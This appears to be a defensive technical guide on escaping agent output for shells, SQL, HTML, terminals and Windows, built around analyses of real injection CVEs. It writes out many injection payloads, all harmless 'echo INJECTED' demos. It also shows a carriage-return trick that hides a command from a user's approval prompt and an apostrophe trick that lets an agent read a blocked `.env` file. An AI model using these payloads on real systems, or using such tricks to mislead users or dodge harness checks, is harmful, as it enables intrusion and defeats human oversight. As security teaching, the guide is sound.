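In SQL, an agent's message should be written as a string literal, enclosed in single quotes with each apostrophe inside it doubled. The text `done'; SELECT 'INJECTED` becomes `'done''; SELECT ''INJECTED'`, which the database stores as a single value. Some databases also give the backslash a special meaning, so the escaping function should come from the database's own library. PostgreSQL, for example, has `quote_literal`.

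Escaping doesn't protect the number 3, just as it didn't protect the card type in the online shop. The harness should convert the text to a number in its own programming language and write that number into the query, rejecting anything that doesn't convert. An integer type is safest, because Python's `float` accepts the text "nan", for "not a number", and writes it back as the letters `nan`, which a database may read as the name of a column. Negative numbers can also break the query. In the template `failures-COUNT`, the value −1 produces `failures--1`, and in most databases two hyphens start a comment that hides the rest of the line. A space before the slot or parentheses around it prevents this.

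Table and column names are identifiers. Standard SQL encloses them in double quotation marks and doubles any that occur inside the name, although MySQL uses backquotes by default and SQL Server also allows square brackets. PostgreSQL's function for quoting identifiers is `quote_ident`. If an agent chooses the column by which to sort a report, `ORDER BY "failures"` sorts by that column, but `ORDER BY 'failures'` specifies a constant string, which does nothing or causes an error, depending on the database. Correct quoting still lets the agent name any column, including one the report should not use, so a harness should check the name against a fixed list.

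Searches can add another interpreter. The SQL operator `LIKE` treats a percent sign in its pattern as "any text" and an underscore as "any one character". Someone searching the log for the exact message "100% done" needs a second kind of escaping inside the string literal:

```
SELECT * FROM log WHERE message LIKE '100!% done' ESCAPE '!'
```

Here the developer has chosen the exclamation mark as the escape character, so each exclamation mark in the message also needs one in front of it. Without this step, the query finds the wrong rows, though it injects no command.

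### Web pages

Many harnesses show progress on a web page, where the same message may appear in several positions. Between tags, "the build didn't finish" needs no change. The special characters there are `<`, which can start a tag, and `&`, which starts a character reference, a code that stands for a character. The correct form of `<b>INJECTED</b>` is:

```
&lt;b&gt;INJECTED&lt;/b&gt;
```

A browser displays HTML character references as the original characters. It decodes the references only after it has found the tags, so a decoded `<` cannot open a new tag. Python's `html.escape` replaces `&`, `<`, `>` and both kinds of quotation mark.

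The original notification may also need this treatment. On many Linux desktops, the program that draws notifications accepts a few HTML-like tags, so a message containing `<b>` may appear in bold. The harness should escape the message first for that program and then for the shell.

An attribute is a named value inside a tag, such as the `title` that appears when the mouse rests on an element. The quotation mark that encloses the value is now special:

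```
<span title='the build didn&#x27;t finish'>Status</span>
```

With an unescaped apostrophe, the value would end after `didn`, and the browser would read the rest as further attributes. An attacker could use that to add an attribute containing a script. The template must have quotation marks around the value, because a space ends an unquoted value and `html.escape` does not change spaces.

Attributes such as `onclick` contain JavaScript, so the browser interprets them twice, first decoding the character references and then parsing the result as a program. In `onclick="show('didn&#x27;t finish')"`, the browser decodes `&#x27;` to an apostrophe before it parses the JavaScript, and the apostrophe ends the string early. As with `ssh`, the harness has to escape twice, first for JavaScript and then for HTML. It is easier to keep outside text out of such attributes.

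Inside a `<script>` element the browser does not decode character references, so `html.escape` would leave `&#x27;` in the message. The value needs the rules for a JavaScript string, and a JSON encoder such as Python's `json.dumps` supplies most of them:

```
<script>const message = "the build didn't finish";</script>
```

A message that contains `</script>` still ends the script element, even inside quotation marks, because the browser looks for the end of the script before JavaScript parses any strings. `json.dumps` does not escape those characters, so the harness should replace every `<` in the JSON with `\u003c`, which JavaScript reads as the same character and HTML does not recognise as the start of a tag.

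In a web address, percent-encoding replaces each special character with a percent sign and the code of each of its bytes. A link that passes the message to a log viewer looks like this:

```
<a href="https://example.com/log?note=the%20build%20didn%27t%20finish">Log</a>
```

In Python, `urllib.parse.quote` with `safe=''` encodes a single value within an address, including any slashes. If the agent supplies the whole address, encoding all of it would break the link, and escaping it for the HTML attribute doesn't change the destination. An address that begins with `javascript:` can contain no special HTML characters, yet a browser may run the rest as a script when someone clicks the link. The harness has to accept only addresses that start with a scheme it expects, usually `https:` or `http:`.

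### Terminals

Command-line harnesses print the agent's text in a terminal. Letters, digits and ordinary punctuation, including the apostrophe, are harmless there. The special characters are the control characters, most of which are invisible. A carriage return moves the cursor to the start of the line, and a backspace moves it one place left. The escape character, ASCII 27, begins longer control sequences. It turns the text red when followed by `[31m` and clears the screen when followed by `[2J`. Other sequences change the window's title, create links whose visible text differs from their destination or, in some terminals, write to the clipboard. Some make the terminal send a reply, which reaches the running program as though the user had typed it.

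These characters matter most when a harness displays a command and asks the user to approve it. Suppose the command is `echo INJECTED #` followed by a carriage return, `ls *.py` and eight spaces. The terminal prints the first part, returns to the start of the line and prints the rest over it, so the user sees only `ls *.py`. If the user approves, the shell runs `echo INJECTED` and ignores the rest, because `#` starts a comment.

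A terminal has no quotation marks or other general way to mark a control character as literal text. The escape character, despite its name, starts commands and doesn't make the text after it literal. No escaping function can therefore satisfy the equation for a message that contains control characters. The harness has to remove them or show them in a visible form, such as `^[` or `\x1b` for the escape character. A visible form is usually better, because the user can see that the text contained control characters. If the harness uses the `\x1b` form, it should also double every real backslash, as Python's `repr` does. Otherwise a message that contains the four characters `\x1b` looks the same as one that contained an escape character.

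The harness should look for control characters rather than known escape sequences. A filter for colour codes misses the sequence that clears the screen, but without the escape character, the terminal shows both as ordinary text. The control characters are codes 0 to 31 and 127 to 159. The upper range is included because some terminals treat code 155 as the escape character followed by an opening bracket. Tabs and line breaks may stay where the layout allows them, but not in a log with one entry per line, where a message containing a line break could look like two entries.

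Unicode also has invisible characters that reverse the direction of text, which can make a command look different from the one that runs. `repr` makes these visible too, but it breaks up emoji that contain an invisible joining character.

### The rules by interpreter

The functions below are from Python's standard library unless the entry names another source.

| Interpreter and position | Special characters | Correct rule | Standard function |
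|---|---|---|---|
| POSIX shell, no quotation marks in the template | Space, tab, line break, quotation marks, backslash, dollar sign, backquote, operators and others | Put the whole value in single quotation marks | `shlex.quote` |
| POSIX shell, single quotation marks | Apostrophe | Close the quotation, add `"'"`, reopen it | `shlex.quote`, after removing the template's own marks |
| POSIX shell, double quotation marks | Dollar sign, backquote, backslash, double quotation mark | Put a backslash before each; not reliable in an interactive Bash | None; end the quotation before the slot and use `shlex.quote` |
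| PowerShell, verbatim string | Apostrophe and its typographic variants | Double each | `EscapeSingleQuotedStringContent` (PowerShell) |
| PowerShell, expandable string | Dollar sign, backtick, double quotation marks | Put a backtick before each | None; use a verbatim string |
| cmd.exe and batch files | Percent sign, double quotation mark, caret, ampersand, pipe, angle brackets, parentheses, exclamation mark, line break | No known rule for every string; reject what cannot be escaped | `Command` (Rust), for batch files |
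| SQL, string literal | Apostrophe; in some databases also backslash | Double the apostrophe and follow the database's own rules for backslashes | `quote_literal` (PostgreSQL) |
| SQL, identifier | Double quotation mark | Enclose in double quotation marks and double any inside; accept only listed names | `quote_ident` (PostgreSQL) |
| SQL, number | Anything that is not part of a number | Convert to a number and write it back | `int` |
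| HTML, text | `&` and `<` | Replace with character references | `html.escape` |
| HTML, ordinary attribute | `&` and the enclosing quotation mark | Enclose in quotation marks and use character references | `html.escape` |
| HTML, string inside a script | Quotation marks, backslash, line breaks, `<` | Encode as JSON, then write `<` as `\u003c` | `json.dumps`, plus the replacement |
| Web address, one value | Everything except unaccented letters, digits, hyphen, full stop, underscore and tilde | Percent-encode, then escape for the attribute | `urllib.parse.quote` with `safe=''` |
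| Terminal | Control characters | No escaped form; remove them or show them visibly | `repr` |

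## Why doubling quotation marks does not stop command injection

Quote-doubling means writing every quotation mark inside a quoted string twice, so that "didn't" becomes `didn''t`. It correctly escapes string literals in standard SQL and also works for PowerShell's verbatim strings, where more kinds of quotation mark must be doubled. Many other interpreters have quoted strings that look the same but follow different rules. In those interpreters, doubling may not stop an attack, and for some messages it creates the vulnerability it was meant to prevent.

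### Why the rule looks complete

A database that follows the SQL standard reads a string literal one character at a time after the opening apostrophe. Any character except an apostrophe goes into the value. At an apostrophe, the database looks at the next character. If that is also an apostrophe, the pair adds one apostrophe to the value and the string continues. Otherwise the string has ended. In the notation below, the bar means "or" and the star means "any number of times":

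```
literal  =  '  ( any character except '  |  '' )*  '
```

Doubling turns each character of a message into one of the two units in the brackets: an apostrophe becomes a pair, and every other character stays as it is. The database reads these units in order and turns each one back into the original character. It can't stop early, because the doubled text contains no apostrophe without a partner. It therefore reaches the template's own closing mark with the whole message as the value. For the message `done'; SELECT 'INJECTED`, the parse is:

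```
'            opens the string
done         ordinary text
''           one apostrophe
; SELECT     ordinary text
''           one apostrophe
INJECTED     ordinary text
'            closes the string
```

This proof covers every message, but it assumes that only an apostrophe can end the string and that no other character changes what an apostrophe means. It also assumes that the slot sits between apostrophes and that the harness and the database divide the bytes into the same characters.

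As with any escaping, the harness must not shorten the message afterwards, because the cut could fall inside a pair.

### Typographic apostrophes in PowerShell

Rclone copies files to and from cloud storage and other servers. It can connect to a server over SFTP, a file-transfer protocol that runs over `ssh`. To verify a copy without downloading it, rclone can have the server compute a hash, a short fingerprint of the file's contents. If the server's shell is PowerShell, rclone requests the hash with a PowerShell command that contains the file's path.

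Rclone (2022) introduced separate quoting for PowerShell and cmd.exe because Windows shells need different rules from Unix ones. The developers therefore knew that they were writing for a different interpreter. Kodem's *CVE-2026-71312* gives the line of code that quoted the path for PowerShell:

```
return "'" + strings.ReplaceAll(shellPath, "'", "''") + "'", nil
```

This puts the path between ASCII apostrophes (the plain keyboard kind) and doubles every ASCII apostrophe inside it. But PowerShell also accepts the typographic marks ‘, ’, ‚ and ‛ (U+2018 to U+201B) as single quotation marks. Any of them can close a string that an ASCII apostrophe opened.

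The same quoting rule would fail in a notification harness. The message `done’; echo INJECTED #` contains no ASCII apostrophe, so doubling leaves it unchanged:

```
./notify.ps1 'done’; echo INJECTED #'
```

PowerShell divides the line like this:

```
./notify.ps1    the script to run
'done’          a string with the value "done"
;               ends the command
echo            a second command
INJECTED        its argument
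#'              a comment
```

The comment sign hides the template's closing apostrophe, which would otherwise cause a syntax error. A harmless message can also fail. Word processors and some language models write "didn’t" with a typographic apostrophe. In this template, PowerShell ends the string after `didn`, then finds a later string that never closes, so it shows no notification.

In rclone, an attacker could put the payload in a file name if they could create or rename files on the server or in a storage source that fed it. When an rclone user ran an operation that computed hashes, the server ran the payload with the permissions of that user's SSH account. The attacker did not need the account's password, but the server had to use PowerShell and allow rclone to run commands.

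The advisory that Kodem reproduces has good evidence for this. The tester passed all four typographic marks through rclone's real quoting function, with a harmless command that created a marker file. A stronger test ran rclone's real hashing code against a simulated SSH session connected to a real PowerShell, using a file name that contained only characters Windows permits. GitLab's *CVE-2026-71312* (2026) rates the severity 8.0 out of 10, and OSV's *GO-2026-6182* (2026) lists both hashing and `About` as affected operations.

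Version 1.75.0, released on 31 July 2026, fixed the flaw. The US government's National Vulnerability Database published its entry, NVD's *CVE-2026-71312 Detail* (2026), on 5 August. According to Miggo's *CVE-2026-71312*, the new code has a replacer named `powerShellQuoteEscaper` that escapes all five marks. PowerShell's rule for the typographic marks is also doubling, as an example in Microsoft's quoting guide shows. The notification then becomes:

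```
./notify.ps1 'done’’; echo INJECTED #'
```

PowerShell reads two typographic apostrophes in a row as one literal apostrophe, and the string continues to the last character of the line. Microsoft's `EscapeSingleQuotedStringContent` doubles all five characters that PowerShell treats as single quotes, but it is a .NET function and rclone is written in Go.

For people who can't upgrade, SecureLayer7's *CVE-2026-71312* suggests either turning off the hash check or setting `shell_type = cmd`. The second suggestion is doubtful because the setting changes how rclone quotes paths but doesn't change the server's shell, so PowerShell would still parse paths quoted for cmd.exe.

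According to Rclone's 1.75.0 release notes, AI agents found an "unprecedented number" of the security issues that the release fixes. Another fix concerns paths with variable expansions or line breaks on servers that use cmd.exe.

### A second escape character in MySQL

By default, the MySQL database reads a doubled apostrophe inside a string as one apostrophe, as the SQL standard requires. It also treats the backslash as an escape character, so `\'` stands for one apostrophe too. These two rules interfere with each other.

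Take the harness that logs each message with the number of failed tests, and this message:

```
done\', 0), ("INJECTED", 0) #
```

The message contains one apostrophe. The harness doubles it and inserts the result into the query:

```
INSERT INTO log (message, failures)
VALUES ('done\'', 0), ("INJECTED", 0) #', 3)
```

MySQL parses the second line as follows:

```
VALUES (             the first row begins
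'                    opens the string
done                 ordinary text
\'                   one apostrophe
'                    closes the string
, 0)                 completes the first row
, ("INJECTED", 0)    adds a second row
#', 3)               a comment
```

MySQL reads the backslash and the first apostrophe of the pair as an escaped apostrophe, so the second apostrophe closes the string. The log gains a row that reads INJECTED, and the first row records zero failed tests instead of three. The payload uses double quotation marks for its own string because default MySQL allows them and the harness doesn't double them. It also stays within one `INSERT` statement, so it still works when a client library doesn't allow two statements to be sent at once.

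In this case, the harness would have been safer if it had left the message unchanged. Without doubling, `\'` would have been an apostrophe in the value, and the string would have continued to the template's closing quotation mark. Doubling added a second apostrophe, which ended the string early. Other messages would break a harness that left them unchanged.

A database that follows the standard treats the backslash in the same query as ordinary text and `''` as a pair, so the string continues up to the apostrophe after `#`. The number 3 follows, as the developer intended. A developer who tests on such a database and deploys on MySQL will not see the flaw in testing.

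Backslashes can also cause problems in messages with no apostrophe. If an agent reports that it saved a file to `C:\logs\`, the final backslash turns the template's closing apostrophe into part of the value, and the query fails. If the folder is `C:\new`, MySQL reads `\n` as a line break and stores the wrong text without an error.

The harness can prevent this by doubling backslashes as well as apostrophes. MySQL then reads `\\''` as one backslash and one apostrophe. But in MySQL's `NO_BACKSLASH_ESCAPES` mode, a backslash is ordinary text, so the extra one stays in the stored value. The right rule therefore depends on a setting that can differ between connections. MySQL's escaping functions take the open connection as an argument so that they can account for its settings.

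PostgreSQL treats a backslash as ordinary text in a plain literal by default, but as an escape character in a literal that starts with `E'`. JavaScript strings and the shell's `$'…'` form also have backslash escapes, so there too a backslash can escape the first apostrophe of a doubled pair, and the second then ends the string.

In PowerShell's expandable strings, the escape character is the backtick. Microsoft gives doubling as one correct way to write a double quotation mark in such a string, and for text that the developer types by hand, it is. But the outside message `` `"; echo INJECTED # `` gets past it:

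```
./notify.ps1 "`""; echo INJECTED #"
```

PowerShell reads the backtick and the first quotation mark after it as one literal quotation mark. The next mark closes the string, and `echo INJECTED` runs.

### Slots where doubling has nothing to act on

The online shop that Su and Wassermann described doubled every apostrophe, but its query included the card type as a number without quotation marks, so an attacker could inject SQL there without using an apostrophe. A shell command has the same weakness if its template leaves a value unquoted. In the template `notify-send Agent MESSAGE`, the message `done; echo INJECTED` contains no quotation mark to double, and the shell runs `notify-send` and then `echo`.

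HTML does not treat a doubled quotation mark as an escaped one, so in `title='the build didn''t finish'` the first apostrophe of the pair ends the value.

If a harness encloses a message in double quotation marks for a POSIX shell and doubles any inside it, `$(echo INJECTED)` stays unchanged and still runs. A backslash works here as well. The message `\"; echo INJECTED #` produces this line:

```
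notify-send Agent "\""; echo INJECTED #"
```

The shell's parse has the same pattern as MySQL's:

```
notify-send    the program
Agent          its first argument
"              opens the string
\"             one double quotation mark
"              closes the string
;              ends the command
echo           a second command
INJECTED       its argument
#"             a comment
```

Cloud CLI, also known as Claude Code UI, made a closely related mistake. It is a third-party interface for Claude Code, Codex and other coding agents, and it lets users set the name that the version-control program Git records with their changes. Kodem's *CVE-2026-31861* reproduces the code:

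```
await execAsync(`git config --global user.name "${gitName.replace(/"/g, '\\"')}"`);
```

This puts a backslash before each double quotation mark instead of doubling it. Within double quotation marks, that is the right treatment for the mark itself, but the code did nothing about the other special characters. With the name `$(echo INJECTED)`, the server runs:

```
git config --global user.name "$(echo INJECTED)"
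```

The shell runs `echo` first, and Git then stores INJECTED as the user's name. NVD's *CVE-2026-31861 Detail* notes that the code also did not escape backslashes. A name beginning with `\"` could therefore end the string early.

An attacker had to be logged in to use this flaw, but the program signed logins with a fixed secret, so anyone could forge one. Version 1.24.0 fixed the injection, and the published remedy starts Git without a shell. Kodem's *CVE-2026-31862* describes further cases in the same program, where file names, branch names and descriptions of code changes, all of which agents routinely write, went into shell commands.

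### The disputed Claude Code case

In March 2026, Anthropic accidentally published the source code of Claude Code. The company Phoenix Security searched it for places where outside text entered shell commands, and reported three. Phoenix Security's *Claude Code leak to vulnerability Three CVEs in Claude Code CLI* (2026) reproduces the code that opened a file in the user's text editor:

```
execSync_DEPRECATED(`${editorCommand} "${filePath}"`, {
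  stdio: 'inherit',
})
```

The path is between double quotation marks, with no escaping. If the editor is `vim` and a file has the name `$(echo INJECTED).txt`, the shell receives this command:

```
vim "$(echo INJECTED).txt"
```

The shell runs `echo INJECTED`, puts the output into the file name, and opens `INJECTED.txt`. Doubling quotation marks would not help, because the original file name contains none. Phoenix Security took the `_DEPRECATED` in the function's name as a sign that Anthropic's developers already considered this kind of call risky.

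This report became CVE-2026-35021, with a severity of 7.8. A change log, *CVE-2026-35021* (2026), shows that the entry was published on 6 April, tagged "disputed" on 13 April and rejected on 29 May. Arawa's *CVE-2026-35021* (2026) names VulnCheck as the organisation that had assigned the number, and says the entry was rejected because the code "cannot be triggered through normal usage of Claude Code".

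Phoenix Security called the flaw confirmed, but its longer account, *Claude Code Critical vulnerability* (2026), describes a narrower test. The testers isolated the pattern and ran it in a "sink-equivalent rig", a stand-in for the vulnerable code. This showed what the shell does with a hostile path, which the POSIX standard already specifies, but not that Claude Code would ever pass such a path to this line. The rejection therefore seems fair.

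Phoenix Security quotes Anthropic's replies only to the other two reports, which Anthropic closed as "Informative". One was about an environment variable, and Anthropic answered that an attacker who controls it must already be able to run code. The other was about login commands in a settings file, which Anthropic said worked as designed. CVELogic's *CVE-2026-35022* (2026) records that the CVE for the settings file was also rejected, because Anthropic's help text warns users to run the non-interactive mode only in trusted folders. Neither reply addresses the quoting in the editor command, which is still a poor pattern to copy.

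### PostgreSQL and malformed text

Developers can avoid most of these mistakes by calling the database's own escaping functions. However, PostgreSQL's *CVE-2025-1094* (2025) describes a flaw in four such functions in libpq, the PostgreSQL client library: `PQescapeLiteral`, `PQescapeIdentifier`, `PQescapeString` and `PQescapeStringConn`. They could fail to neutralise a quotation mark in text that was not valid in its character encoding.

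UTF-8, the usual encoding, stores an apostrophe or an unaccented letter as one byte, and other characters as two to four. The first byte of a longer character indicates its length in bytes. In malformed text, an apostrophe can follow such a byte in place of the rest of the character. An escaping function that relies on the indicated length treats the apostrophe as part of the character and doesn't double it. A program that examines the apostrophe separately will treat it as a quotation mark.

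The second program in this case was psql, PostgreSQL's command-line tool for typing queries or running them from a script. Besides SQL, psql has commands of its own that begin with a backslash, and `\!` passes the rest of the line to the operating system's shell. With ▒ for the stray first byte, an affected function could produce this line:

```
SELECT '▒'; \! echo INJECTED #'
```

An affected version of psql reads it as follows:

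```
SELECT                an SQL keyword
'                     opens the string
▒                     a malformed character
'                     closes the string
;                     ends the query
\!                    runs the rest of the line in a shell
echo INJECTED #'      the shell command, ending in a comment
```

The text has passed from SQL through psql to a shell, although the developer only wanted to store a string. A database server that receives a query directly has no `\!` command and normally rejects malformed UTF-8. This is why PostgreSQL's advisory says the libpq flaw affects only applications that use the escaped text to build input for psql. The advisory also covers a related flaw in PostgreSQL's command-line utilities, which requires particular combinations of Chinese and multilingual encodings.

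The security company Rapid7 found the PostgreSQL flaw while studying an attack on BeyondTrust's remote-support products, according to its *CVE-2025-1094* (2025). In every scenario its researchers tested, running code on the target also required exploiting the PostgreSQL flaw. BeyondTrust's December 2024 patch blocked the whole attack in its own products but did not fix the cause in PostgreSQL. Rapid7 reported the flaw, which has a severity score of 8.1, on 27 January 2025, and PostgreSQL published fixes on 13 February in versions 17.3, 16.7, 15.11, 14.16 and 13.19.

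A harness can also reject malformed text before escaping anything. In Python, `data.decode('utf-8')` raises an error if the bytes in `data` are not valid UTF-8. The model's messages usually reach the harness as valid text, but file names and the output of other programs can contain almost any bytes. Windows can also convert a harmless character into a quotation mark after the harness has escaped the text.

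### The apostrophe that disappears

POSIX single quotation marks look like the place where doubling should fail worst, since the shell has no rule that a pair stands for one apostrophe. Here is the attack on the original notification, with its apostrophes doubled:

```
notify-send 'Agent' 'done''; echo ''INJECTED'
```

The shell parses the second argument like this:

```
'done'         a string
'; echo '      a string joined to it
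'INJECTED'     a string joined to that
```

The notification reads "done; echo INJECTED", and nothing else runs. The first apostrophe of each pair closes the string and the second immediately opens a new one, so no character of the message falls outside the quotation marks. A backslash has no special meaning between single quotation marks, so this holds for any message, and doubling does stop command injection in this position.

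But both apostrophes have gone. The honest message suffers in the same way:

```
notify-send 'Agent' 'the build didn''t finish'
```

The user sees "the build didnt finish". In terms of the equation for correct escaping, the command keeps its structure but the value changes. A developer who tests only for the word INJECTED on a line of its own will conclude that the function works.

A missing apostrophe hardly matters in a notification, but in a file name it can make a command act on the wrong file. If an agent wants to delete `Bob's notes.txt`, the harness produces `rm 'Bob''s notes.txt'`, and the shell passes `Bobs notes.txt` to `rm`. If a file with that name exists, `rm` deletes it instead.

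The loss can also defeat a check. Suppose a harness lets an agent read files with `cat`, but refuses the name `.env`, because files with that name often contain passwords. The agent asks for `.e'nv`, which is a different name and passes the check. The harness then doubles the apostrophe:

```
cat '.e''nv'
```

The shell joins the two strings and `cat` prints `.env`, so the agent has read the forbidden file. This isn't command injection, because the shell runs only one `cat` command with one argument. `shlex.quote` would have preserved the apostrophe, and `cat` would have looked for a file that probably doesn't exist.

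### Results by interpreter

In this table, "safe" means every valid message arrives unchanged as a single value. "Lossy" means the message can't break out of its string but may arrive altered, and "injectable" means some message can change the command or query.

| Interpreter and position | Mark doubled | Result | Reason |
|---|---|---|---|
| Standard SQL, string literal | Apostrophe | Safe | A pair stands for one apostrophe |
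| Standard SQL, identifier | Double quotation mark | Safe | A pair stands for one quotation mark |
| SQL, number | Apostrophe | Injectable | The slot has no quotation marks around it |
| MySQL in default mode, string literal | Apostrophe | Injectable | A backslash frees the second apostrophe |
| PostgreSQL before the February 2025 fixes, escaped text sent through psql | Apostrophe | Injectable | Malformed UTF-8 can hide an apostrophe from the escaping function |
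| PowerShell, verbatim string | ASCII apostrophe only | Injectable | Four typographic marks also close the string |
| PowerShell, verbatim string | All five single quotation marks | Safe | A pair stands for one mark |
| PowerShell, expandable string | Double quotation mark | Injectable | `$(…)` still runs, and a backtick frees the second mark |
| POSIX shell, single quotation marks | Apostrophe | Lossy | The shell joins the strings and drops the apostrophe |
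| POSIX shell, double quotation marks | Double quotation mark | Injectable | `$(…)` and backquotes still run, and a backslash frees the second mark |
| POSIX shell, no quotation marks | Either | Injectable | A semicolon can start a new command |
| cmd.exe, double quotation marks | Double quotation mark | Injectable | Variables expand before cmd.exe processes quotation marks |
| HTML, quoted attribute | The enclosing mark | Injectable | The first mark of the pair ends the value |
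| JavaScript, quoted string | The enclosing mark | Injectable | A backslash frees the second mark |

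## Why removing dangerous characters is fragile

Developers who distrust an escaping rule often delete the dangerous characters instead. If the harness removes every apostrophe from a status message, the message can't close the single quotation marks in the notification command. This stops command injection in that template, though it also turns "didn't" into "didnt". Deletion fails when a filter removes sequences instead of single characters, when a developer reuses the filter for another interpreter, or when another program changes the text afterwards.

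### Deleting a sequence can create it

Suppose the template puts the message between double quotation marks, and the harness deletes `$(`, the two characters that start a command substitution in a shell:

```
message.replace('$(', '')
```

This turns `$(echo INJECTED)` into `echo INJECTED)`, which is harmless. But consider a message with both characters written twice:

```
$$((echo INJECTED)
```

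Python finds one `$(` in the middle of `$$((echo INJECTED)` and deletes it. The remaining `$` and `(` join to form `$(echo INJECTED)`, which the shell runs. A filter that deletes `../` from file paths has the same problem, because it turns `....//` into `../`.

The usual fix is to repeat the deletion until the text stops changing. Each deletion shortens the text, so the loop must end, and the final text can't contain `$(`. But it can still contain other dangerous syntax. The message `` `echo INJECTED` `` uses the shell's older notation for the same substitution and passes unchanged. If the filter deletes several sequences, the loop has to repeat all the deletions together. A filter that deletes every `$(` and only then every `../` turns `$../(echo INJECTED)` into `$(echo INJECTED)`.

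Deleting single characters never has this fault, because removing one character can't create another. Replacing each forbidden sequence with a space also avoids it, as long as no forbidden sequence contains a space, because the space separates the text on either side.

DOMPurify, a widely used JavaScript library for making HTML safe, replaced sequences with spaces and still had the fault. One of its options is for pages built with frameworks such as Vue 2, which evaluate any expression between double curly brackets. The option removes such expressions from outside text. Docker Scout's *CVE-2026-41239* explains how one could survive, and a harmless version looks like this:

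```
{<foo></foo>{"INJECTED"}<foo></foo>}
```

The parser divides this into three pieces of text separated by `foo` elements. DOMPurify checked each piece on its own and found no double brackets. It also removed the `foo` elements, which it doesn't permit, and the pieces joined to form `{{"INJECTED"}}`. A second check over the whole result would have caught this, but DOMPurify ran that check only when an application requested a string, not when it requested the DOM, the browser's tree of page elements.

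OSV's *CVE-2026-41239* (2026) dates the record to 23 April and gives 3.4.0 as the first fixed version. The fix joins neighbouring pieces of text before checking them, but expressions could still form inside `<template>` elements until version 3.4.8, according to INCIBE's *CVE-2026-65900* (2026), an entry from Spain's cybersecurity institute. GitLab's *Advisories for Npm/Dompurify package* also lists the same fault in shadow roots, which are separate trees attached to an element.

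### A list fits one interpreter and one position

A developer might decide that the dangerous characters in a shell are the semicolon, ampersand, pipe, dollar sign, backquote and angle brackets. With the template `notify-send Agent MESSAGE`, this two-line message contains none of them:

```
done
echo INJECTED
```

The shell ends the first command at the line break and runs the second line as a new command. Adding the line break to the list of characters to remove prevents this, but the shell still expands an asterisk in the message into file names.

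A list of dangerous characters that is complete for this template can be wrong for another. This one omits the percent sign, which is dangerous in cmd.exe, and the typographic apostrophes that are dangerous in PowerShell, which rclone's developers overlooked. Inside single quotes in a POSIX shell, all the characters on the list are harmless, and the only dangerous one, the apostrophe, is missing from it.

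Removing every character on any interpreter's list of dangerous characters would strip out most punctuation and still not be enough. In Su and Wassermann's example of an online shop, a customer named John sends the word `cardtype`, which contains only lower-case letters, instead of a number. The condition `cardtype=2` becomes `cardtype=cardtype`, which is true for every card with a type, so he gets all his cards instead of one kind.

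### WorstFit

Filters and escaping functions rely on the interpreter receiving exactly the text they produced. *WorstFit* (Tsai and Splitline, 2025) showed that Windows can turn harmless characters into quotation marks, backslashes and hyphens after a program has correctly escaped its text.

Early versions of Windows stored text using code pages, which are tables of characters for particular languages. Windows moved to Unicode in the mid-1990s but kept the old functions so that existing programs would still work. Many functions therefore come in two versions. The one whose name ends in W returns Unicode, and the one ending in A converts the text to the computer's code page. If the code page lacks a character, Windows may substitute a similar-looking one in a process called best-fit conversion. On an English-language system, `√π⁷≤∞` becomes `vp7=8`.

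Now suppose a Python harness starts `notify.exe` directly, without a shell, and passes the message as one argument. The message contains two fullwidth quotation marks (U+FF02), which are wide versions of the ordinary mark for East Asian text:

```
done＂ ＂INJECTED
```

Python builds the single command line that Windows requires, and puts ordinary quotation marks around the message because of the space. It leaves the fullwidth marks alone, which is correct, since they have no special meaning on a Windows command line:

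```
notify.exe "done＂ ＂INJECTED"
```

If `notify.exe` then asks for its command line with `GetCommandLineA`, Windows converts the string first:

```
notify.exe "done" "INJECTED"
```

The program receives two arguments instead of one. An attacker can make the second an option, and some programs have options that start other programs. Tsai and Splitline found such cases in `wget`, `openssl` and the `tar.exe` that comes with Windows. The web-based file manager elFinder escaped every argument it passed to `tar.exe`, but an attacker who chose an archive's name could still run a command on the server.

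The programmer who wrote `notify.exe` may not know about `GetCommandLineA`. A C program that starts with the ordinary `main` function gets its arguments from startup code that the compiler adds, and that code uses the old conversion.

Which characters are dangerous depends on the computer's language settings. The fullwidth mark becomes a real one on the Thai code page and on the group that covers European languages, Hebrew, Arabic and Vietnamese. On the Japanese code page the yen sign becomes a backslash, and on the Korean one the won sign does. This affects messages that contain an ordinary quotation mark, such as `done¥" INJECTED`. Python escapes the mark with a backslash, and the conversion then supplies another:

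```
"done¥\" INJECTED"     as Python wrote it
"done\\" INJECTED"     as the program reads it
```

The program reads the two backslashes as one literal backslash, so the quotation mark ends the argument. Doubling quotation marks fails in MySQL for much the same reason.

File paths can change in this way too. Cuckoo Sandbox runs suspected malware in a virtual machine and copies out the files it creates. Its official version still depended on Python 2.7, which used the old functions for some paths. Malware could create a file with yen signs in its name. When someone downloaded that file through the web interface, the host read the yen signs as backslashes, followed the path out of the folder and sent Cuckoo's own configuration file.

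Tsai and Splitline conclude that no programming language's standard library can fully prevent this, because the conversion happens inside the receiving program. That program's developers can fix it by using the W functions and `wmain`, the Unicode version of `main`, but they may have to rewrite all their argument-handling code. Microsoft made this fix in the copy of the download tool curl that it ships with Windows, while the curl project's own Windows build remained affected. Users can also switch Windows to UTF-8, an option that was still in beta when the research appeared. A harness that can't avoid an affected program can restrict the argument to ASCII, but it will then reject names like José.

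Hardly anyone wanted to take responsibility for the problem. Curl's author called curl "a victim here, not the responsible party". Microsoft replied that a program which puts untrusted input into a command line is already vulnerable. This argument is weak, because Python had followed Microsoft's quoting rules exactly. Microsoft initially rejected all three of the researchers' reports, but later fixed the Excel issue and added a warning to the documentation for `GetCommandLineA`.

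Yason (2013) had already described how the conversion defeated a filter in Java Web Start, a program for launching Java applications, by turning a different lookalike character into a quotation mark.

### A filter that held for twelve years

The WorstFit research began with a filter for a single character. In 2012, PHP-CGI, a program that runs PHP scripts for a web server, had a flaw. The Apache web server passed it the part of a web address after the question mark as a command-line argument, so a visitor who wrote `-s` there got the page's source code, and other options could run code on the server. PHP's developers fixed this with a check that skipped any leading spaces and ignored the options if the next character was a hyphen.

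Nobody broke the check for 12 years. Then Tsai and Splitline tried a soft hyphen (U+00AD), a usually invisible character that marks where a word may be divided. On the Chinese and Japanese code pages, Windows converts it to an ordinary hyphen. The check, which looked for an ordinary hyphen at the start of the text, missed the soft hyphen, and PHP's option parser received the converted character. This flaw became CVE-2024-4577. The vulnerability database GCVE (2024) records that it was exploited by 12 June 2024, three days after it became public.

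PHP's developers released a fix in June 2024 but had to release another later that year. According to a second GCVE entry (2024), attackers could still get past the first fix on computers with certain unusual code-page settings.

The 2012 check had the same weakness because it examined the text before the last conversion, although it didn't delete anything. Developers can also make this mistake when Windows isn't involved. If a harness filters a message for `$(` and then decodes its percent-encoding, the text `%24%28` passes the filter and becomes `$(`. Any filter therefore has to run on the text in its final form.

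### What stripping does to honest text

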